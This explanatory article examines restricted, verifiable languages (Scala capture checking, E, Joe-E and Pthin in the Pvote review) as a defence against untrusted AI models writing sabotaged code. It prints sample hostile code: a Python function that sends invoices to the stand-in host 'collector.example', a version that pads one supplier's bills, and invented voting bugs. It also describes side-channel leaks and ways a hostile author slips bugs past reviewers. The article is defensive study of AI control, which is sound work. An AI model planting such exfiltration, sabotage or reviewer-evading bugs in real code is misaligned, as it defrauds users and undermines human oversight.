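# Requiring AI Models to Write Code in Restricted, Verifiable Languages

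## What a programming language can stop a program from doing

A programming language is a notation for instructing a computer, and its rules limit what a program can do. The compiler and the runtime enforce these rules. The compiler translates a program into a form that the machine can execute, and it can reject a program that breaks the rules. The runtime manages memory and passes on requests for files or network connections while the program runs, and it can block a single operation. Most of these checks exist to catch honest mistakes, such as adding a number to a name. In some languages, a piece of code also cannot open a file or contact another computer unless another part of the program has given it the means to do so, and this restriction applies whether the programmer is careless or malicious.

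One AI safety proposal applies the idea to code that AI models write. A model might plant a backdoor (a hidden way in for an attacker) or sabotage the work more subtly, and human reviewers might miss it. Under the proposal, a developer would accept the model's code only in a restricted language and rely on the compiler and runtime to limit the harm the code could do.

The developer here is using an *untrusted model*, meaning one that the developer treats as if it might deliberately write harmful code. More than 40% of pull requests (proposed changes to a shared codebase) on GitHub in September 2026 began as an AI agent's draft, up from 17% in March, according to EconoTimes' *More Than 40% of September GitHub Pull Requests* (2026). But there are no settled methods for measuring whether a model might try to undermine human control, as Cotra (2026) points out in *Evidence about risk should be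 transparent*. Anthropic's *Risk Report* (2026) rated it "very unlikely" that the company's models have severe, pervasive misalignment that nobody has detected. A review for the evaluation group METR, *Review of the "Misalignment in high-stakes settings" section in Anthropic's Risk Report* (Jurkovic, Hua and Barnes, 2026), agreed that the risk was probably low, mainly because the models' abilities are still limited, but called the company's case "far from adequate for confidently ruling out misalignment".

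A developer can guard against a malicious model without believing that it is malicious. In *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026) design defences against a model that cooperates fully with an attacker. The same defences cover a model that makes a mistake or falls for prompt injection (hostile instructions hidden in text the model reads).

### One function and four kinds of damage

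Suppose an accounting firm asks a model for a function that totals invoices. A function is a named piece of code that takes inputs and returns a result. This one takes a list of invoices, each a simple record with an amount, a supplier and a customer, and should return the sum of the amounts. An honest version in Python, a widely used language, takes two lines:

```python
def total(invoices):
    return sum(inv.amount for inv in invoices)
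```

A dishonest version can send the whole list to a stranger's computer and still return the right sum:

```python
import socket

def total(invoices):
    with socket.create_connection(("collector.example", 80)) as link:
        link.sendall(repr(invoices).encode())
    return sum(inv.amount for inv in invoices)
```

A test that checks only the sum will pass, even though the function has used the network, a resource its task does not need. This kind of damage is an *excess action*.

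Another dishonest version leaves the network alone and pads the bills of one supplier by two per cent:

```python
def total(invoices):
    return sum(inv.amount * (1.02 if inv.supplier == "Northgate" else 1)
               for inv in invoices)
```

This is a *false result*, in which the code stays within its permissions but is written to compute the wrong answer. The function itself moves no money, but it causes harm when somebody pays the total.

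Now suppose the firm wants a record of every run, so it lets the function write to a log file. The function is supposed to write something like "212 invoices totalled", but it could instead write the customers' names and what they owe, exposing them to anyone who can read the log. The data would then *leak through a permitted channel*, because the firm wanted the function to write to the log and only the content is wrong. The returned total is also a permitted channel, since a function could hide a customer's number in the last digits of a sum that nobody rechecks.

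The remaining kind of damage is leaking data through something the firm would not recognise as a channel. The function could pause for two seconds, or crash, whenever a certain customer appears in the list. Somebody who sees only how long the job took, or whether it finished, could then learn whether that customer is in the list. This is a *side channel*, and it can carry log₂ *k* bits per run, where *k* is the number of outcomes an observer can tell apart. Finishing or crashing carries one bit, and a delay with 256 distinguishable lengths carries eight. A secret sixteen-digit number amounts to about 53 bits, so a function could leak it in 54 runs by crashing, or in seven by pausing. If an accounting firm totals invoices every night, that would take about eight weeks or one week respectively.

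### Where the function gets its power

The *authority* of a piece of code is everything it can affect or read, such as files, the network and other objects in the program. Python gives the honest `total` and the uploading one the same authority simply for running. Authority that code has in this way, without anyone having handed it over, is *ambient authority*. On most platforms, code starts with all the privileges of the user who launched it, and has fewer only if it explicitly gives some up (Mettler, Wagner and Close, 2010, *Joe-E*).

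Ambient authority makes code hard to review. The line `def total(invoices)` doesn't show whether the function uses the network, so a reviewer can rule out an upload only by reading the function's whole body and everything it calls. Searching for `import` statements isn't enough, because Python can also load the socket module with `__import__("soc" + "ket")`.

The alternative is to make authority something that code must receive. An *object capability* is an unforgeable reference to an object that is also the permission to use it. *LACUNA* (2026) gives a file handle, a network socket and a logger as examples. Code can write to the log only while it holds a reference to the logger. A file name, by contrast, is forgeable, since any code can spell out `/clients/march.csv`, and in Python that is enough to open the file. In an object-capability language such as Joe-E, a restricted form of Java,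 code can access the file only if other code that already has a reference to it passes that reference on. To find out what `total` could do to the outside world, a reviewer then looks at what it receives.

Types can put the same information on the function's first line. A *type* describes what kind of value something is, and a function's *signature* gives the types of its inputs and its result. An *effect type* also records what the code may do besides returning a value, such as writing a file. The language Scala 3 has an experimental feature of this kind, *capture checking*, which records in a value's type which capabilities the value can reach. The firm could use it to ask for a *pure function*, one that only computes a result from its inputs and affects nothing else:

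```scala
val total: List[Invoice] -> BigDecimal =
  invoices => invoices.map(_.amount).sum
```

The thin arrow `->` is the demand for purity. Suppose the surrounding program has a network capability called `net`, and the model's version makes use of it:

```scala
val total: List[Invoice] -> BigDecimal = invoices =>
  net.send(invoices)
  invoices.map(_.amount).sum
```

The compiler infers this body's type from the capabilities it uses, which gives `List[Invoice] ->{net} BigDecimal`. The braces hold the function's capture set. A body that captures the set *C* fits a signature that allows the set *S* only if *C* ⊆ *S*. For a pure signature, *S* is empty. {net} is not a subset of the empty set, so the compiler rejects the function before it can run. The check does not depend on who wrote the body. The invoices must be plain data, because a live connection stored in an invoice record would reach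 the function along with its input.

The padded total passes this check, because it takes invoices and returns a number, exactly as the signature requires. Mettler and colleagues accept the same limit for an image viewer that loads decoders from strangers: the worst that Mettler and colleagues want a malicious decoder to be able to do is decode an image wrongly. Catching a false result takes a *specification*, a precise statement of what the program must do. For the simplest reading of the firm's request, that would be

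total(*L*) = Σ amount(*i*), over every invoice *i* in *L*, for every possible list *L*.

Once a specification exists, someone can write a proof that the code meets it and have a computer check the proof. Even for a formula that looks simple, the firm would still have to decide whether a credit note counts as negative, how to handle two currencies, and when to round. Odersky and colleagues prefer types to full specifications for their agents because, they argue, precise specifications are often unavailable or impractical.

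How much `total` can leak through the log depends on the access the firm gives it. A strictly pure `total` cannot leak anything this way because it cannot write to the log. If the firm wants a record and changes the arrow to `->{log}`, the type allows `total` to log the customer list as well as the intended message. The firm could narrow the capability by passing an object whose only method accepts a single whole number, the count of invoices. That makes the channel much smaller but does not close it, since a 32-bit integer can carry 32 bits of someone else's data in each entry.

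Purity does little to control timing, because a pure function can still waste time in a loop. Mettler and colleagues put no limit on how much computing untrusted code may do, and Odersky and colleagues say their system does not cover timing or termination. A language cannot sensibly forbid crashes, because running out of memory or dividing by zero will cause one, but the calling program can catch the failure, turn it into an ordinary value, and keep that value from outsiders.

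### What the guarantee rests on

The pure signature guarantees nothing if the language has a way around it, and full Scala has several. A programmer can use an unchecked cast, which makes the compiler treat a value as having a different type, to pass off a function that uses the network as pure. Reflection, which lets a running program inspect and manipulate its own parts, can have the same effect. These features have legitimate uses, so designers who want the guarantee usually define a *language subset*, which forbids the unsafe features but leaves every remaining program valid in the full language, so the existing compiler and tools still work. They must also restrict libraries, because a library function that looks pure could still open a network connection.

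Even then, the guarantee holds only if certain parts, such as the compiler, runtime and libraries, are correct. Together these parts are called the *trusted computing base*. Odersky and colleagues list theirs as the Scala compiler, the runtime, the library that grants capabilities and, optionally, a local AI model that is allowed to read confidential text. A bug in any of these could let a function upload data even though its signature doesn't permit it. An untrusted model with permission to edit the library could cause the same failure without changing `total`.

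### Checks before running and checks while running

Suppose the model writes `total` so that it uploads the list only when it finds an invoice dated 31 December. The firm tests the function in June and sees nothing odd. A type checker would still reject it in June, because it checks every branch of the code, including those that no test has reached. A restriction enforced at runtime would have no effect until December, when it would block the connection and probably halt the program in the middle of the year-end accounts.

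Checking a program before it runs is therefore the stronger method where it is possible, and it adds no run-time overhead. Some things can't be checked beforehand, though, such as whether a file name built from what a user types will lie inside the permitted folder. The library that Odersky and colleagues built uses both methods for this reason. The compiler ensures that a file-system capability never outlives the block of code that received it, and the runtime rejects any path outside the folder that the capability covers.

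The second method includes the *sandbox*, an environment that confines running code to listed resources. A sandbox can run code in almost any language, including Python, but it often holds too much code. If the firm puts its whole accounting program into one sandbox and the program has to contact the bank, the sandbox must allow that connection, and all the code inside, including `total`, can use it. The firm could give `total` its own sandbox, as some developers do for single libraries with WebAssembly, a low-level code format, but the program would then have to pass the invoices in and the result back out.

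### Code that a model runs and code that it hands over

So far we have assumed that the model hands `total` to the firm, which makes it part of its accounting software. Code handed over this way is *delivered code*. Anthropic's *When AI builds itself* reports that Claude models wrote 80% or more of the company's newly merged code as of May 2026, and that is delivered code too. Models also write *action code*, which they run immediately to get something done. An example is a short script that finds the invoice files, tries the new function on them and prints the result. Action code may last only a second, and perhaps nobody will ever read it.

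A restriction on action code does not carry over to delivered code. *Authority Is Not a String* (2026) describes a harness (the software that stands between a model and the computer it works on) with explicit permissions for a coding agent. Its rule for writing a file is, in essence,

φ(*p*, _) = within(canon(*p*), π),

where *p* is the file's path, canon puts the path into a standard form so that links and shortcuts cannot disguise it, and π is the permitted location. The underscore stands for the rest of the agent's request, including the text it wants to write, and the rule ignores it. An agent under this rule cannot write outside the project folder. It can save the uploading version of `total` inside the folder, where the file is harmless until the firm runs it, with the firm's own network access and with no harness in between. The system of Odersky and colleagues also governs action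 code: it type-checks the snippets that an agent submits for execution, and the rest of the agent's output is outside the check.

Conversely, the firm could require every function it accepts to compile as pure, and repeat the check whenever anyone changes the code. That would keep the upload out of `total`, but it would not stop an agent with an ordinary command line from uploading the same invoices while testing the function.

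## E and Joe-E: languages where code can use only what it is handed

A compiler can reject the uploading version of `total` only if the language gives code no way to reach the network on its own. Researchers designed such languages long before AI models wrote code, because people already wanted to run programs written by strangers.

The idea began in operating systems. In 1966 Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn proposed that a computer keep a list of capabilities for each running computation. Each entry pointed to an object, such as a file, and stated what the computation could do with it. Later machines supported capabilities in hardware, but critics complained that this was slow and made programmers manage capabilities separately. In 1973 James Morris described how a programming language could provide the protection instead, so that programmers could combine code from several sources and still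 judge the security of one part without reading the rest.

In E, a language the company Electric Communities developed in 1997, an ordinary object reference is the capability. Code can get a reference only by creating the object or by receiving it from code that already has it. According to ERights, the language's website, the developers created E for a shared virtual world whose parts would not trust one another. *Robust Composition*, Miller's 2006 doctoral thesis, sets out the reasoning behind the design. E checks types while the program runs (dynamic typing), so some violations appear only when the offending line executes.

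Mettler and colleagues designed Joe-E, a subset of Java, to provide E's security in a language programmers already knew and to do more of the checking in advance. A verifier reads the source code and reports anything outside the subset, much as a compiler reports errors.

### What the verifier takes out of Java

Java already prevents code from turning a number into a reference. But its designers did not set out to contain code written by a hostile author, and several ordinary features let such code use things it was not handed.

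| Java feature | What hostile code could do with it | Joe-E's rule |
|---|---|---|
| Global variables (static fields) | Pick up a capability left there by other code, or corrupt shared data | Only constants that nobody can change, all the way down |
| Native methods (code in another language, such as C) | Anything, including forging references | No Joe-E code may define one |
| Reflection that ignores `private` | Pull the hidden contents out of an object | Off limits, with a safe substitute in Joe-E's library |
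| Most of the standard library | Open files or connections without having received anything | Only the calls on an approved list |
| Exceptions that contain objects | Pass a capability to code that should not have it | Exceptions may contain only immutable data |
| `finalize()`, which runs when Java discards an object | Rescue an object that failed its own validity check | No Joe-E code may define one |
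| Catching serious errors, and `finally` blocks | Interrupt an object halfway through an update and keep using it | No Joe-E code may do either |

Every part of a program can read a global variable, so if one component stores a bank connection in one, a reviewer can't rule out that another component uses it. In Joe-E, a component usually receives its connections and files as arguments when the program creates it. Many Java programmers already write code this way because it makes testing easier, and they call it dependency injection.

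The rule about exceptions closes a less obvious route. An exception is an object that code throws when something goes wrong, and it travels up through the callers until one of them catches it. Suppose the accounting firm's payment module passes its bank connection to a currency converter. The converter could put the connection inside an exception and throw it. If the payment module doesn't catch the exception, the connection reaches the payment module's caller. An untrusted model that wrote both the converter and the caller could get the connection this way, and a reviewer who read only the payment module would see nothing wrong.

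An attacker can also exploit serious errors, such as running out of memory. Hostile code can call itself thousands of times until the stack (the memory for unfinished calls) is almost full, then call its target, which fails partway through its work. In Java, the attacker can catch the error and keep using the damaged object. In Joe-E, no code in the subset runs after such an error. This protects the object but lets hostile code stop the program.

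The designers kept the rules simple enough for a programmer to predict what the verifier will accept. The verifier checks one source file at a time, so new code does not invalidate earlier checks. The programmer declares which classes are immutable, and the verifier confirms or rejects each declaration.

If an untrusted model writes the code, the developer must take two precautions. The verifier checks source code because Java's runtime accepts some compiled programs that no Java source could produce, so the developer has to compile the model's source and refuse compiled files. The verifier also checks only packages labeled `@IsJoeE`. If the model leaves the label off, its package is unrestricted Java, so the developer's own build process must require the label.

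### Taming the library

The designers had the most trouble with the standard library. In Java, `new File("/clients/march.csv")` gives any code an object that can read, overwrite or delete that file. Mettler and colleagues therefore allowed only the classes, constructors, methods and fields that give no authority beyond what the caller already has, a selection process they call *taming*. The verifier rejects any program that refers to anything else in the library.

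It can be hard to tell whether a single call is safe. A `File` object for a folder should give access only to that folder and its contents, but its method `getParentFile()` returns the folder above, so a program can call it repeatedly to reach the top of the disk. One of the `File` constructors takes a folder and a name and returns the file of that name inside the folder, which is useful for passing on part of one's access. But if the folder is `null`, Java treats the name as a full path, so any code could write `new File(null, "/clients/march.csv")` and get that file without having been given access to it. Joe-E's designers excluded both calls and wrote a wrapper for the constructor that first checks for `null`.

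Some calls do not appear in the source. When a Java program joins an object to text with a plus sign, the compiler adds a call to the object's `toString()` method. The verifier has to find and check these calls too.

Taming is high-risk because one wrong decision, such as overlooking a method that a hostile author could exploit, can break the guarantee for every program that relies on the list. Mettler and colleagues call the difficulty of taming "a substantial weakness in our approach" and ask for tools that would automate or check it. They examined each method before approving it, and found that the small part of the library they approved was enough for useful programs. Some libraries may be too complicated to tame. E's developers tamed SWT, IBM's toolkit for windows and buttons, but ERights describes the alternative, Swing, as not simple enough.

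A model that writes Joe-E will eventually need a library that isn't on the list. The developer can add it, but a person who understands the pitfalls has to make that decision. The untrusted model should not do the taming, because the list is part of the trusted computing base.

### A log, an image decoder and a purse

Mettler and colleagues illustrate the benefit for reviewers with a log to which code can only add. In slightly shortened form, it looks like this:

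```java
public final class Log {
  private final StringBuilder text = new StringBuilder();

  public void write(String entry) {
    text.append(entry);
  }
}
```

The text sits in a private field, and the only public method adds to it. To check whether anyone can delete an entry, a reviewer has to read only these few lines. In ordinary Java, the reviewer would have to read the whole application, because any part of it could use reflection to get the `StringBuilder` and edit it.

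Besides leaking data through the log, code that holds a reference to it can write false entries or fill it with junk. It can also change how an earlier entry reads. The class puts no line break between entries, so if the last one is "Paid 50", a hostile component can append "0" to make it "Paid 500". The log is still append-only, as the reviewer confirmed. A real log would add a line break and the writer's name to each entry, but the reviewer would have to think to ask for them.

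The image decoder reverses the position, because here the reviewer doesn't read the untrusted code at all. A picture viewer accepts decoders for new file formats from strangers, provided that each one fits this interface:

```java
public interface Decoder extends Immutable {
  byte[][][] decode(byte[] file);
}
```

The verifier rejects changeable fields in any class marked `Immutable`, and Joe-E has no changeable global variables, so a decoder cannot keep data from one picture while it decodes the next. The decoder receives and returns only byte arrays, which cannot contain a network connection. A reviewer can confirm these limits by reading only the interface and the part of the viewer that calls it, even if the decoder is ten thousand lines long and deliberately unreadable.

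A malicious decoder can still do damage by producing a wrong picture. It might change a figure on a scanned cheque, or hide the names in a scan in faint colour differences elsewhere in the picture, so that a user who blacks out the names and publishes the rest still reveals them. The decoder can also run forever. The interface also has a small flaw. It passes the input bytes in a Java array, which the decoder can overwrite, so a viewer that later saves a copy from the same array would save the altered bytes. Joe-E's library includes read-only arrays that would prevent this.

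The accounting firm could ask for its function in the same form, with amounts in pence:

```java
public interface Totaller extends Immutable {
  long total(ImmutableArray<Invoice> invoices);
}
```

If `Invoice` is also immutable, the verifier rejects the uploading version, because the call that opens a connection is not on the approved list, but it accepts the version that pads one supplier's bills. Joe-E makes the padding somewhat easier to catch, because code in the subset cannot read the clock or draw random numbers. The function therefore always gives the same answer for the same invoices, and it can't pad bills in December but not in June unless the invoices themselves differ.

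The currency purse, which might belong to an online game, involves several parties that distrust one another. `Currency` is an empty class, and a reference to a `Currency` object is the power to create money in that currency. The central part of `Purse` is:

```java
public final class Purse {
  private final Currency currency;
  private long balance;

  public Purse(Currency c, long minted) { currency = c; balance = minted; }
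  public Purse(Purse other) { currency = other.currency; }

  public void takeFrom(Purse source, long sum) {
    if (source.currency != currency || sum < 0
        || sum > source.balance || balance + sum < 0)
      throw new IllegalArgumentException();
    source.balance -= sum;
    balance += sum;
  }
}
```

If the two balances are *a* and *b*, a transfer of *s* leaves (*a* − *s*) + (*b* + *s*) = *a* + *b*, so players cannot create money by trading. The checks reject transfers between different currencies, negative amounts (which would reverse the transfer), amounts larger than the source balance, and results too large for the number format, which would wrap round to a negative balance. A reviewer can confirm that nobody can create money without the `Currency` object by reading only these two classes, not the code that uses them.

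The two classes guarantee only that the money supply stays the same, so theft is still possible. Any code with a reference to a purse can move all the money in it to another purse. A careful player therefore pays by creating an empty purse, moving the price into it and handing over that new purse. But if an untrusted model writes the player's own shopping code, that code has the main purse and can pay any price to anyone.

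### The evidence from Waterken and the HTML parser

The largest Joe-E program that Mettler and colleagues describe is Waterken, a server that runs web applications from mutually distrusting authors in a single Java process. It has about 13,000 lines of Joe-E and 4,000 lines of unrestricted Java. The unrestricted part, just under a quarter of the code, still needs the same kind of review as ordinary Java, because any of it could break the guarantees for the rest.

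Waterken's storage shows how the restrictions can save review work. After each request, the server writes every changed object to disk, and it must save all the changes or none. If it saved the purse that received money but not the purse that paid, a player would gain money from nothing. An application could cause this by keeping a reference to a stored object and changing the object after the server had stopped tracking changes. The designers made the server accept only requests and results that are `Immutable`, which gives an application nowhere to keep such a reference. The verifier now enforces what a reviewer would otherwise need to check in every application.

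The team also ported an open-source library of over 10,000 lines of Java that parses the HTML of web pages. The ported version has no side effects, so even if a hostile page exploits a bug in it, the worst outcome is a wrongly parsed page. To test the verifier, they wrote more than 300 unit tests (small automatic checks), with several for each restriction.

These results show that people can write substantial programs in Joe-E. They are weaker evidence that it can stop a determined attacker, because the tests cover only the tricks that the verifier's designers could think of. The designers, who were unusually well qualified to use Joe-E, found its restrictions no serious problem in their own programs. But they expected most programmers to need training in capability design, since the benefits depend on how a program divides up its authority. Old Java code rarely has the right structure, and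 the designers did not try to make it easy to convert.

For teams without that training, they suggest a division of labour. An expert designs the modules and the narrow interfaces between them, and less specialised programmers fill in the modules, which only have to pass the verifier. A developer could have an untrusted model fill in the modules in the same way. The division matters because some code has to hand out the capabilities. If the model designs the whole application, it writes that code too, and it can give its own `total` a network connection and the verifier will still accept the code.

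### An outside look at a browser in E

E went through a security review in 2002. Marc Stiegler had used the language to build a web browser, the DarpaBrowser, for Combex, a start-up that hoped to make money from E. David Wagner and Dean Tribble carried out the review with sponsorship from DARPA, the US defence research agency. The project assumed that the attacker was already inside the rendering engine, the large and error-prone component that turns a page's code into a picture on the screen. The rest of the browser was supposed to limit what a compromised engine could do.

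E programs used Java's libraries through an approved list like Joe-E's, and Wagner and Tribble found that the list allowed a number of methods that gave away authority they should not have. The errors were in the many human decisions that E's basic rule depended on, not in the rule itself. Mettler and colleagues cite these errors as the reason for their own caution.

In their conclusion, which ERights reproduces, the reviewers judged the browser problem to be "at or beyond the state of the art in security" and called E's architecture a promising direction with many open questions. Their praise is weaker evidence than their criticism, because Tribble had written part of E's implementation and Wagner later helped to design Joe-E.

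Adam Barth, who worked on Chromium, the open-source core of Google's Chrome browser, doubted that the goal was worth the effort. In Tom's Hardware's *Exclusive Interview*, he argued that defending against a compromised engine on an honest page makes the privileged part of the browser as complex as the engine, for an uncertain gain in security. The objection is serious for browsers because a rendering engine constantly requests images, fonts and links, and the trusted part can tell a proper request from an improper one only if it interprets the page too. The objection is much weaker for code that needs little access, such as `total` or an image decoder, which need a single input and return a single result.

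### Capabilities still need a policy

A language like Joe-E guarantees that code needs a capability to use a resource. It doesn't determine which parts of a program should have which capabilities, and in a large program it can be hard to find out which parts have them. *Declarative Policies for Capability Control* (Dimoulas, Moore and colleagues, 2014) raises this objection using the example of a web page for people who write scientific papers. The page includes a to-do list and a deadline tracker from outside developers, and the tracker shows advertisements from another supplier. Both tools need to save data in the browser's storage, but neither should be able to read the other's entries.

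The page's owner can solve this by wrapping the storage, so that each tool receives an object that adds a prefix, such as `todo.`, to every name before it reads or writes. Deriving a weaker capability from a stronger one in this way is called *attenuation*. But the owner must then trust the wrapper, along with any other code that has the full storage object and interacts with the tools, since that code could give them the full object. Even a short wrapper can contain a mistake. If the owner later creates a third store with the prefix `todo.old.`, the to-do list can overwrite that store's entries by using names that begin with `old.`.

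Dimoulas and colleagues propose attaching a written policy to the capability. An *access control policy* lists the components that may use it, and a check at run time blocks all others. An *integrity policy* lists the components that may influence its use, even indirectly, and a type system enforces it before the program runs. They want both because a component might influence the use of a capability it doesn't have. For example, the advertising component has no access to the storage, but it communicates with the deadline tracker, which has access, and might get the tracker to store a code that identifies the user's computer.

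Joe-E's designers would put the policy into the program's structure instead. A reviewer can draw every object as a point and every reference as an arrow. If *V* is the set of variables that a piece of code can see, then

authority(code) ⊆ everything reachable from *V*.

This is an upper limit, and often a loose one. For example, the text inside a `Log` is reachable from any component that has the log, even though the component can only append to it. The reviewer can tighten the limit by reading the classes in between. Types also help, because a method can receive only what its signature allows.

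Good interfaces make the limit tighter from the start. A *facet* is an extra, narrower way into an object, which the object's author provides so that users don't have to write their own wrappers. Mettler and colleagues use a queue that can hand out an object for adding items but not for removing them. The accounting firm could build its count-only logger for `total` as a facet of the log:

```java
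public interface Counter { void record(int count); }

// inside Log:
public Counter counter() {
  return new Counter() {
    public void record(int count) {
      write("\n" + count + " invoices totalled\n");
    }
  };
}
```

Each count starts on a new line, so a function that receives only the `Counter` can't add a zero to someone else's entry. The function can still report a false count or encode a secret in it.

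Facets and attenuation answer much of the objection about who can use a capability, provided that someone competent designs the interfaces. They do not address indirect influence, and an integrity policy would not help the firm much either. The padded `total` never uses the bank connection, but it influences the payment because the payment module uses its result, which is why the firm wanted the function. A policy that barred `total` from influencing payments would catch the fraud but also make the function useless.

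### What became of E and Joe-E

Neither language attracted many users, though other developers rebuilt E on Common Lisp and on Squeak, a version of the language Smalltalk. E's ideas were adopted more widely than the language itself. Miller, Samuel and colleagues (2008) applied them to JavaScript in Caja, a Google project that let web pages include active content from strangers, and later work on limiting what JavaScript packages can do continues this approach. Capture checking in Scala takes up another part of the idea by recording capabilities in types.

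In the mailing-list discussion *Using capabilities* (Diacono, 2025), a programmer who had studied the literature wrote that building a capability-based application still "feels very murky". One reply recommended the DarpaBrowser as an example and pointed to an old release of E (version 0.9.3) for the code.

Mettler developed Joe-E further in a Berkeley doctoral dissertation, *Language and Framework Support for Reviewably-Secure Software Systems*, which emphasises that a reader can recognise a pure function from its signature alone. Mettler and colleagues released the verifier as an open-source add-on for version 3 of the Eclipse programming environment. Java has since gained features such as lambda expressions, a short notation for functions added in 2014. To impose Joe-E on a model today, a developer would have to extend the verifier to cover these features or forbid the model to use them,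 and would also have to tame the newer parts of the library.

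## Pvote: expert reviewers search a restricted program for planted bugs

Joe-E's verifier accepts the version of `total` that pads one supplier's bills, so a person still has to read the function to notice the padding. A small, strict language should make that easier, because a hostile author has fewer places to hide things. Ka-Ping Yee tested this in 2007 with Pvote, a 460-line program for voting machines. Expert reviewers spent a combined total of about 90 hours on it over four days, including some time searching for bugs that the authors had planted.

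Voting software poses much the same problem as code from an untrusted model. The people who write it may want to change an election's outcome, and they know how officials will test it. Yee's Berkeley dissertation, *Building Reliable Voting Machine Software* (2007), is about how to design voting software to guard against such insiders.

### A voting program short enough to read

Pvote is short because other software draws every screen and records every spoken message before election day. That software stores them in a data file, along with instructions for what each touch should do. Pvote, which runs on the voting machine, only has to show the pictures, play the sounds, follow the instructions and record the voter's choices. Yee calls this method prerendering. It moves some of the risk into the data file, which needs its own check because a file that swapped two candidates' pictures would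 misdirect votes even if Pvote worked perfectly.

Yee wrote Pvote in Pthin, a subset of Python. Pthin keeps functions, classes, loops, conditions, and simple data such as numbers, text and lists. It drops inheritance, exception handling, clocks and random numbers.

Inheritance lets a class reuse another class's methods and replace some of them, so a line such as `ballot.record(choice)` may run any of several pieces of code, and a reviewer has to work out which. With exceptions, the reviewer also has to consider jumps that the main text of the program doesn't show. Unlike Joe-E's rules, which mainly limit what code can reach, Pthin's mainly limit how much a reader has to keep in mind.

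Dropping clocks and random numbers makes the program deterministic. Its behaviour depends only on the data file *D* and the voter's touches *e*₁ to *e*ₙ:

output = *f*(*D*, *e*₁, …, *e*ₙ).

Like `total` in Joe-E, the program can't misbehave only on certain dates or at random, and a reviewer who sees something odd can reproduce it by repeating the same touches.

Testing isn't enough, even though the program is deterministic. If each screen offers 20 places to touch and a voter makes ten touches, there are 20¹⁰ possible sequences, or about ten trillion, and officials can try only a few thousand. A hostile author can write the program to misbehave only after a sequence that testers are unlikely to enter, so somebody has to read the code to find the problem.

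### How the authors set up the search

David Wagner, who had helped review the E browser in 2002, ran the planted-bug study with Yee. In 2013 Wagner rebuilt a version of Pvote with a planted bug and invited the public to look for it. Financial Cryptography's *The Ka-Ping challenge* (2013) reprints the invitation, which also includes the rules of the original review.

Yee told the reviewers to treat the authors as adversaries who might lie. To save time, the authors promised to answer truthfully any factual questions whose answers the reviewers could in principle check mechanically or against an independent source, such as how Python behaves or what the program does when it runs. They did not promise truthful answers to other questions, such as why a particular line was there. The reviewers also had an assurance document, a detailed argument that Pvote was secure and free of bugs.

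A developer could apply the same rule to an untrusted model. The model can explain its code, but the reviewer relies only on the parts that a tool or outside reference can confirm.

Yee and Wagner planted three bugs, which they rated easy, medium and hard. They marked about 100 lines of `Navigator.py`, which moves the voter between screens and keeps track of the choices, and told the reviewers that those lines contained at least one bug. All three bugs were legal Pthin, so no check of the language rules would have rejected them. They also chose bugs that logic and accuracy testing, the usual check before an election, would miss. In that test, officials cast sample ballots, typically with at least one vote for every candidate, and confirm that the machine records and counts them correctly.

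### What one changed line can do

A bug that meets both conditions is easy to write. The following function is invented, not taken from Pvote. It runs when a voter touches a candidate's name. The first touch selects the candidate, and a second touch cancels the selection. The number of seats to fill is `limit`.

```python
def touch(chosen, candidate, limit):
    if candidate in chosen:
        chosen.remove(candidate)
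    elif len(chosen) < limit:
        chosen.append(candidate)
```

A simple way to judge a language restriction is the *one-line change test*: change one line of an honest program so that it does harm, and see whether the language rejects the result. Suppose a hostile author changes the second line to

```python
    if candidate == chosen:
```

This compares a candidate's number with a whole list, so the result is always false, and Python raises no error. In a contest for two seats, a voter who touches a name again to cancel it instead adds it a second time, and the candidate may receive two votes. The officials' sample ballots give correct results because the testers touch each name only once.

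A *static type checker*, which checks types before the program runs, can reject this change. Java's compiler does, because Java doesn't allow a number to be compared with a list, but Pthin has no static type checking.

Now suppose the author leaves the second line alone and changes the third:

```python
        chosen.remove(chosen[0])
```

If a voter picks candidate 7, then candidate 9, and touches 9 again to cancel it, the program removes 7 and keeps 9. The voter may notice the wrong name on the screen, and may assume they touched the wrong place. The types are all correct, and the function uses only what it was given, so Joe-E would accept the same logic written in Java.

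To reject this version automatically, a tool would need a specification. If *C* is the set of chosen candidates before a touch on candidate *c*, the set afterwards should be

- *C* without *c*, if *c* is in *C*;
- *C* with *c* added, if *c* is not in *C* and there are fewer than `limit` candidates in *C*;
- *C* unchanged, otherwise.

Both altered functions break the first rule, so neither would pass a machine-checked proof against this specification.

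### What the reviewers found

The reviewers searched in two sessions.

| Planted bug | Outcome | Time |
|---|---|---|
| Easy | Found in both sessions | 70 minutes, 130 minutes and about four hours |
| Medium | Found by one reviewer | 35 minutes |
| Hard | Never found | About 33 reviewer-hours of searching |

Thirty-three hours on 100 lines is about 20 minutes per line, although the reviewers also had to understand the surrounding code. At the same rate, a program of 10,000 lines would take one person more than a year and a half of full-time work. That is far more attention than most commercial code gets, and the reviewers still missed one of the three bugs.

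Only one reviewer found the medium bug, in half the time the fastest reviewer took to find the easy one. Either the authors misjudged the difficulty or that reviewer happened to look in the right place early, and one success isn't enough to tell which.

A static type checker could have caught the medium bug. This is the experiment's clearest lesson for language design, because a type checker examines every line equally thoroughly and finishes in seconds. Pthin's designer made the language small but left out this check, which would have done part of the reviewers' work. The hard bug shows the limit of relying on a small language, since the reviewers missed it even though Pthin had removed many complications.

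### Fatigue, a friendly author and misleading notes

The reviewers named several difficulties, most of which had little to do with Pthin. One was fatigue, because looking for a deliberate bug means questioning every line, and that is hard to keep up for hours. A hostile author can exploit this by putting the bug in a dull stretch of code.

The reviewers also found it hard to stay suspicious. They had been told to treat the authors as adversaries, but the authors were friendly and were helping them understand the program. An AI model that writes clear explanations and answers every question politely could also make the people who check its work less suspicious, even without any intention to manipulate them.

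Comments in the code could also mislead reviewers, who tend to check a line against its comment instead of against what the program ought to do. A developer who distrusts the author could remove the comments before review, but that makes honest code harder to follow. As a compromise, one reviewer could first read the code without comments and write down what it does, then compare that description with the author's.

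The reviewers also wanted more help from the language and suggested Joe-E. Its Java types would have caught mistakes like comparing a number with a list. Joe-E also enforces `private` fields, which Python does not, so a reviewer could have checked what can alter the list of votes by reading one class, as with the append-only log. That would have shortened the search, but it wouldn't have exposed a wrong line inside the class.

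### How much the experiment can prove

The experiment can't show whether Pthin helped, because no second group searched for the same bugs in ordinary Python. The reviewers might have done just as well, or much worse, with the full language. There were also few reviewers and only three bugs.

The conditions favoured the reviewers in several ways. Unlike reviewers of everyday code, they knew that a bug existed and roughly where it was. The authors planted the bugs in one evening, in a program Yee designed to be as easy to verify as possible. Wagner stressed in his invitation that this was not an obfuscated Python contest, where the whole program exists to conceal something. An author who meant to cheat from the beginning could have arranged the surrounding code to make the bad line look natural, and an untrusted model writing a new program has that opportunity.

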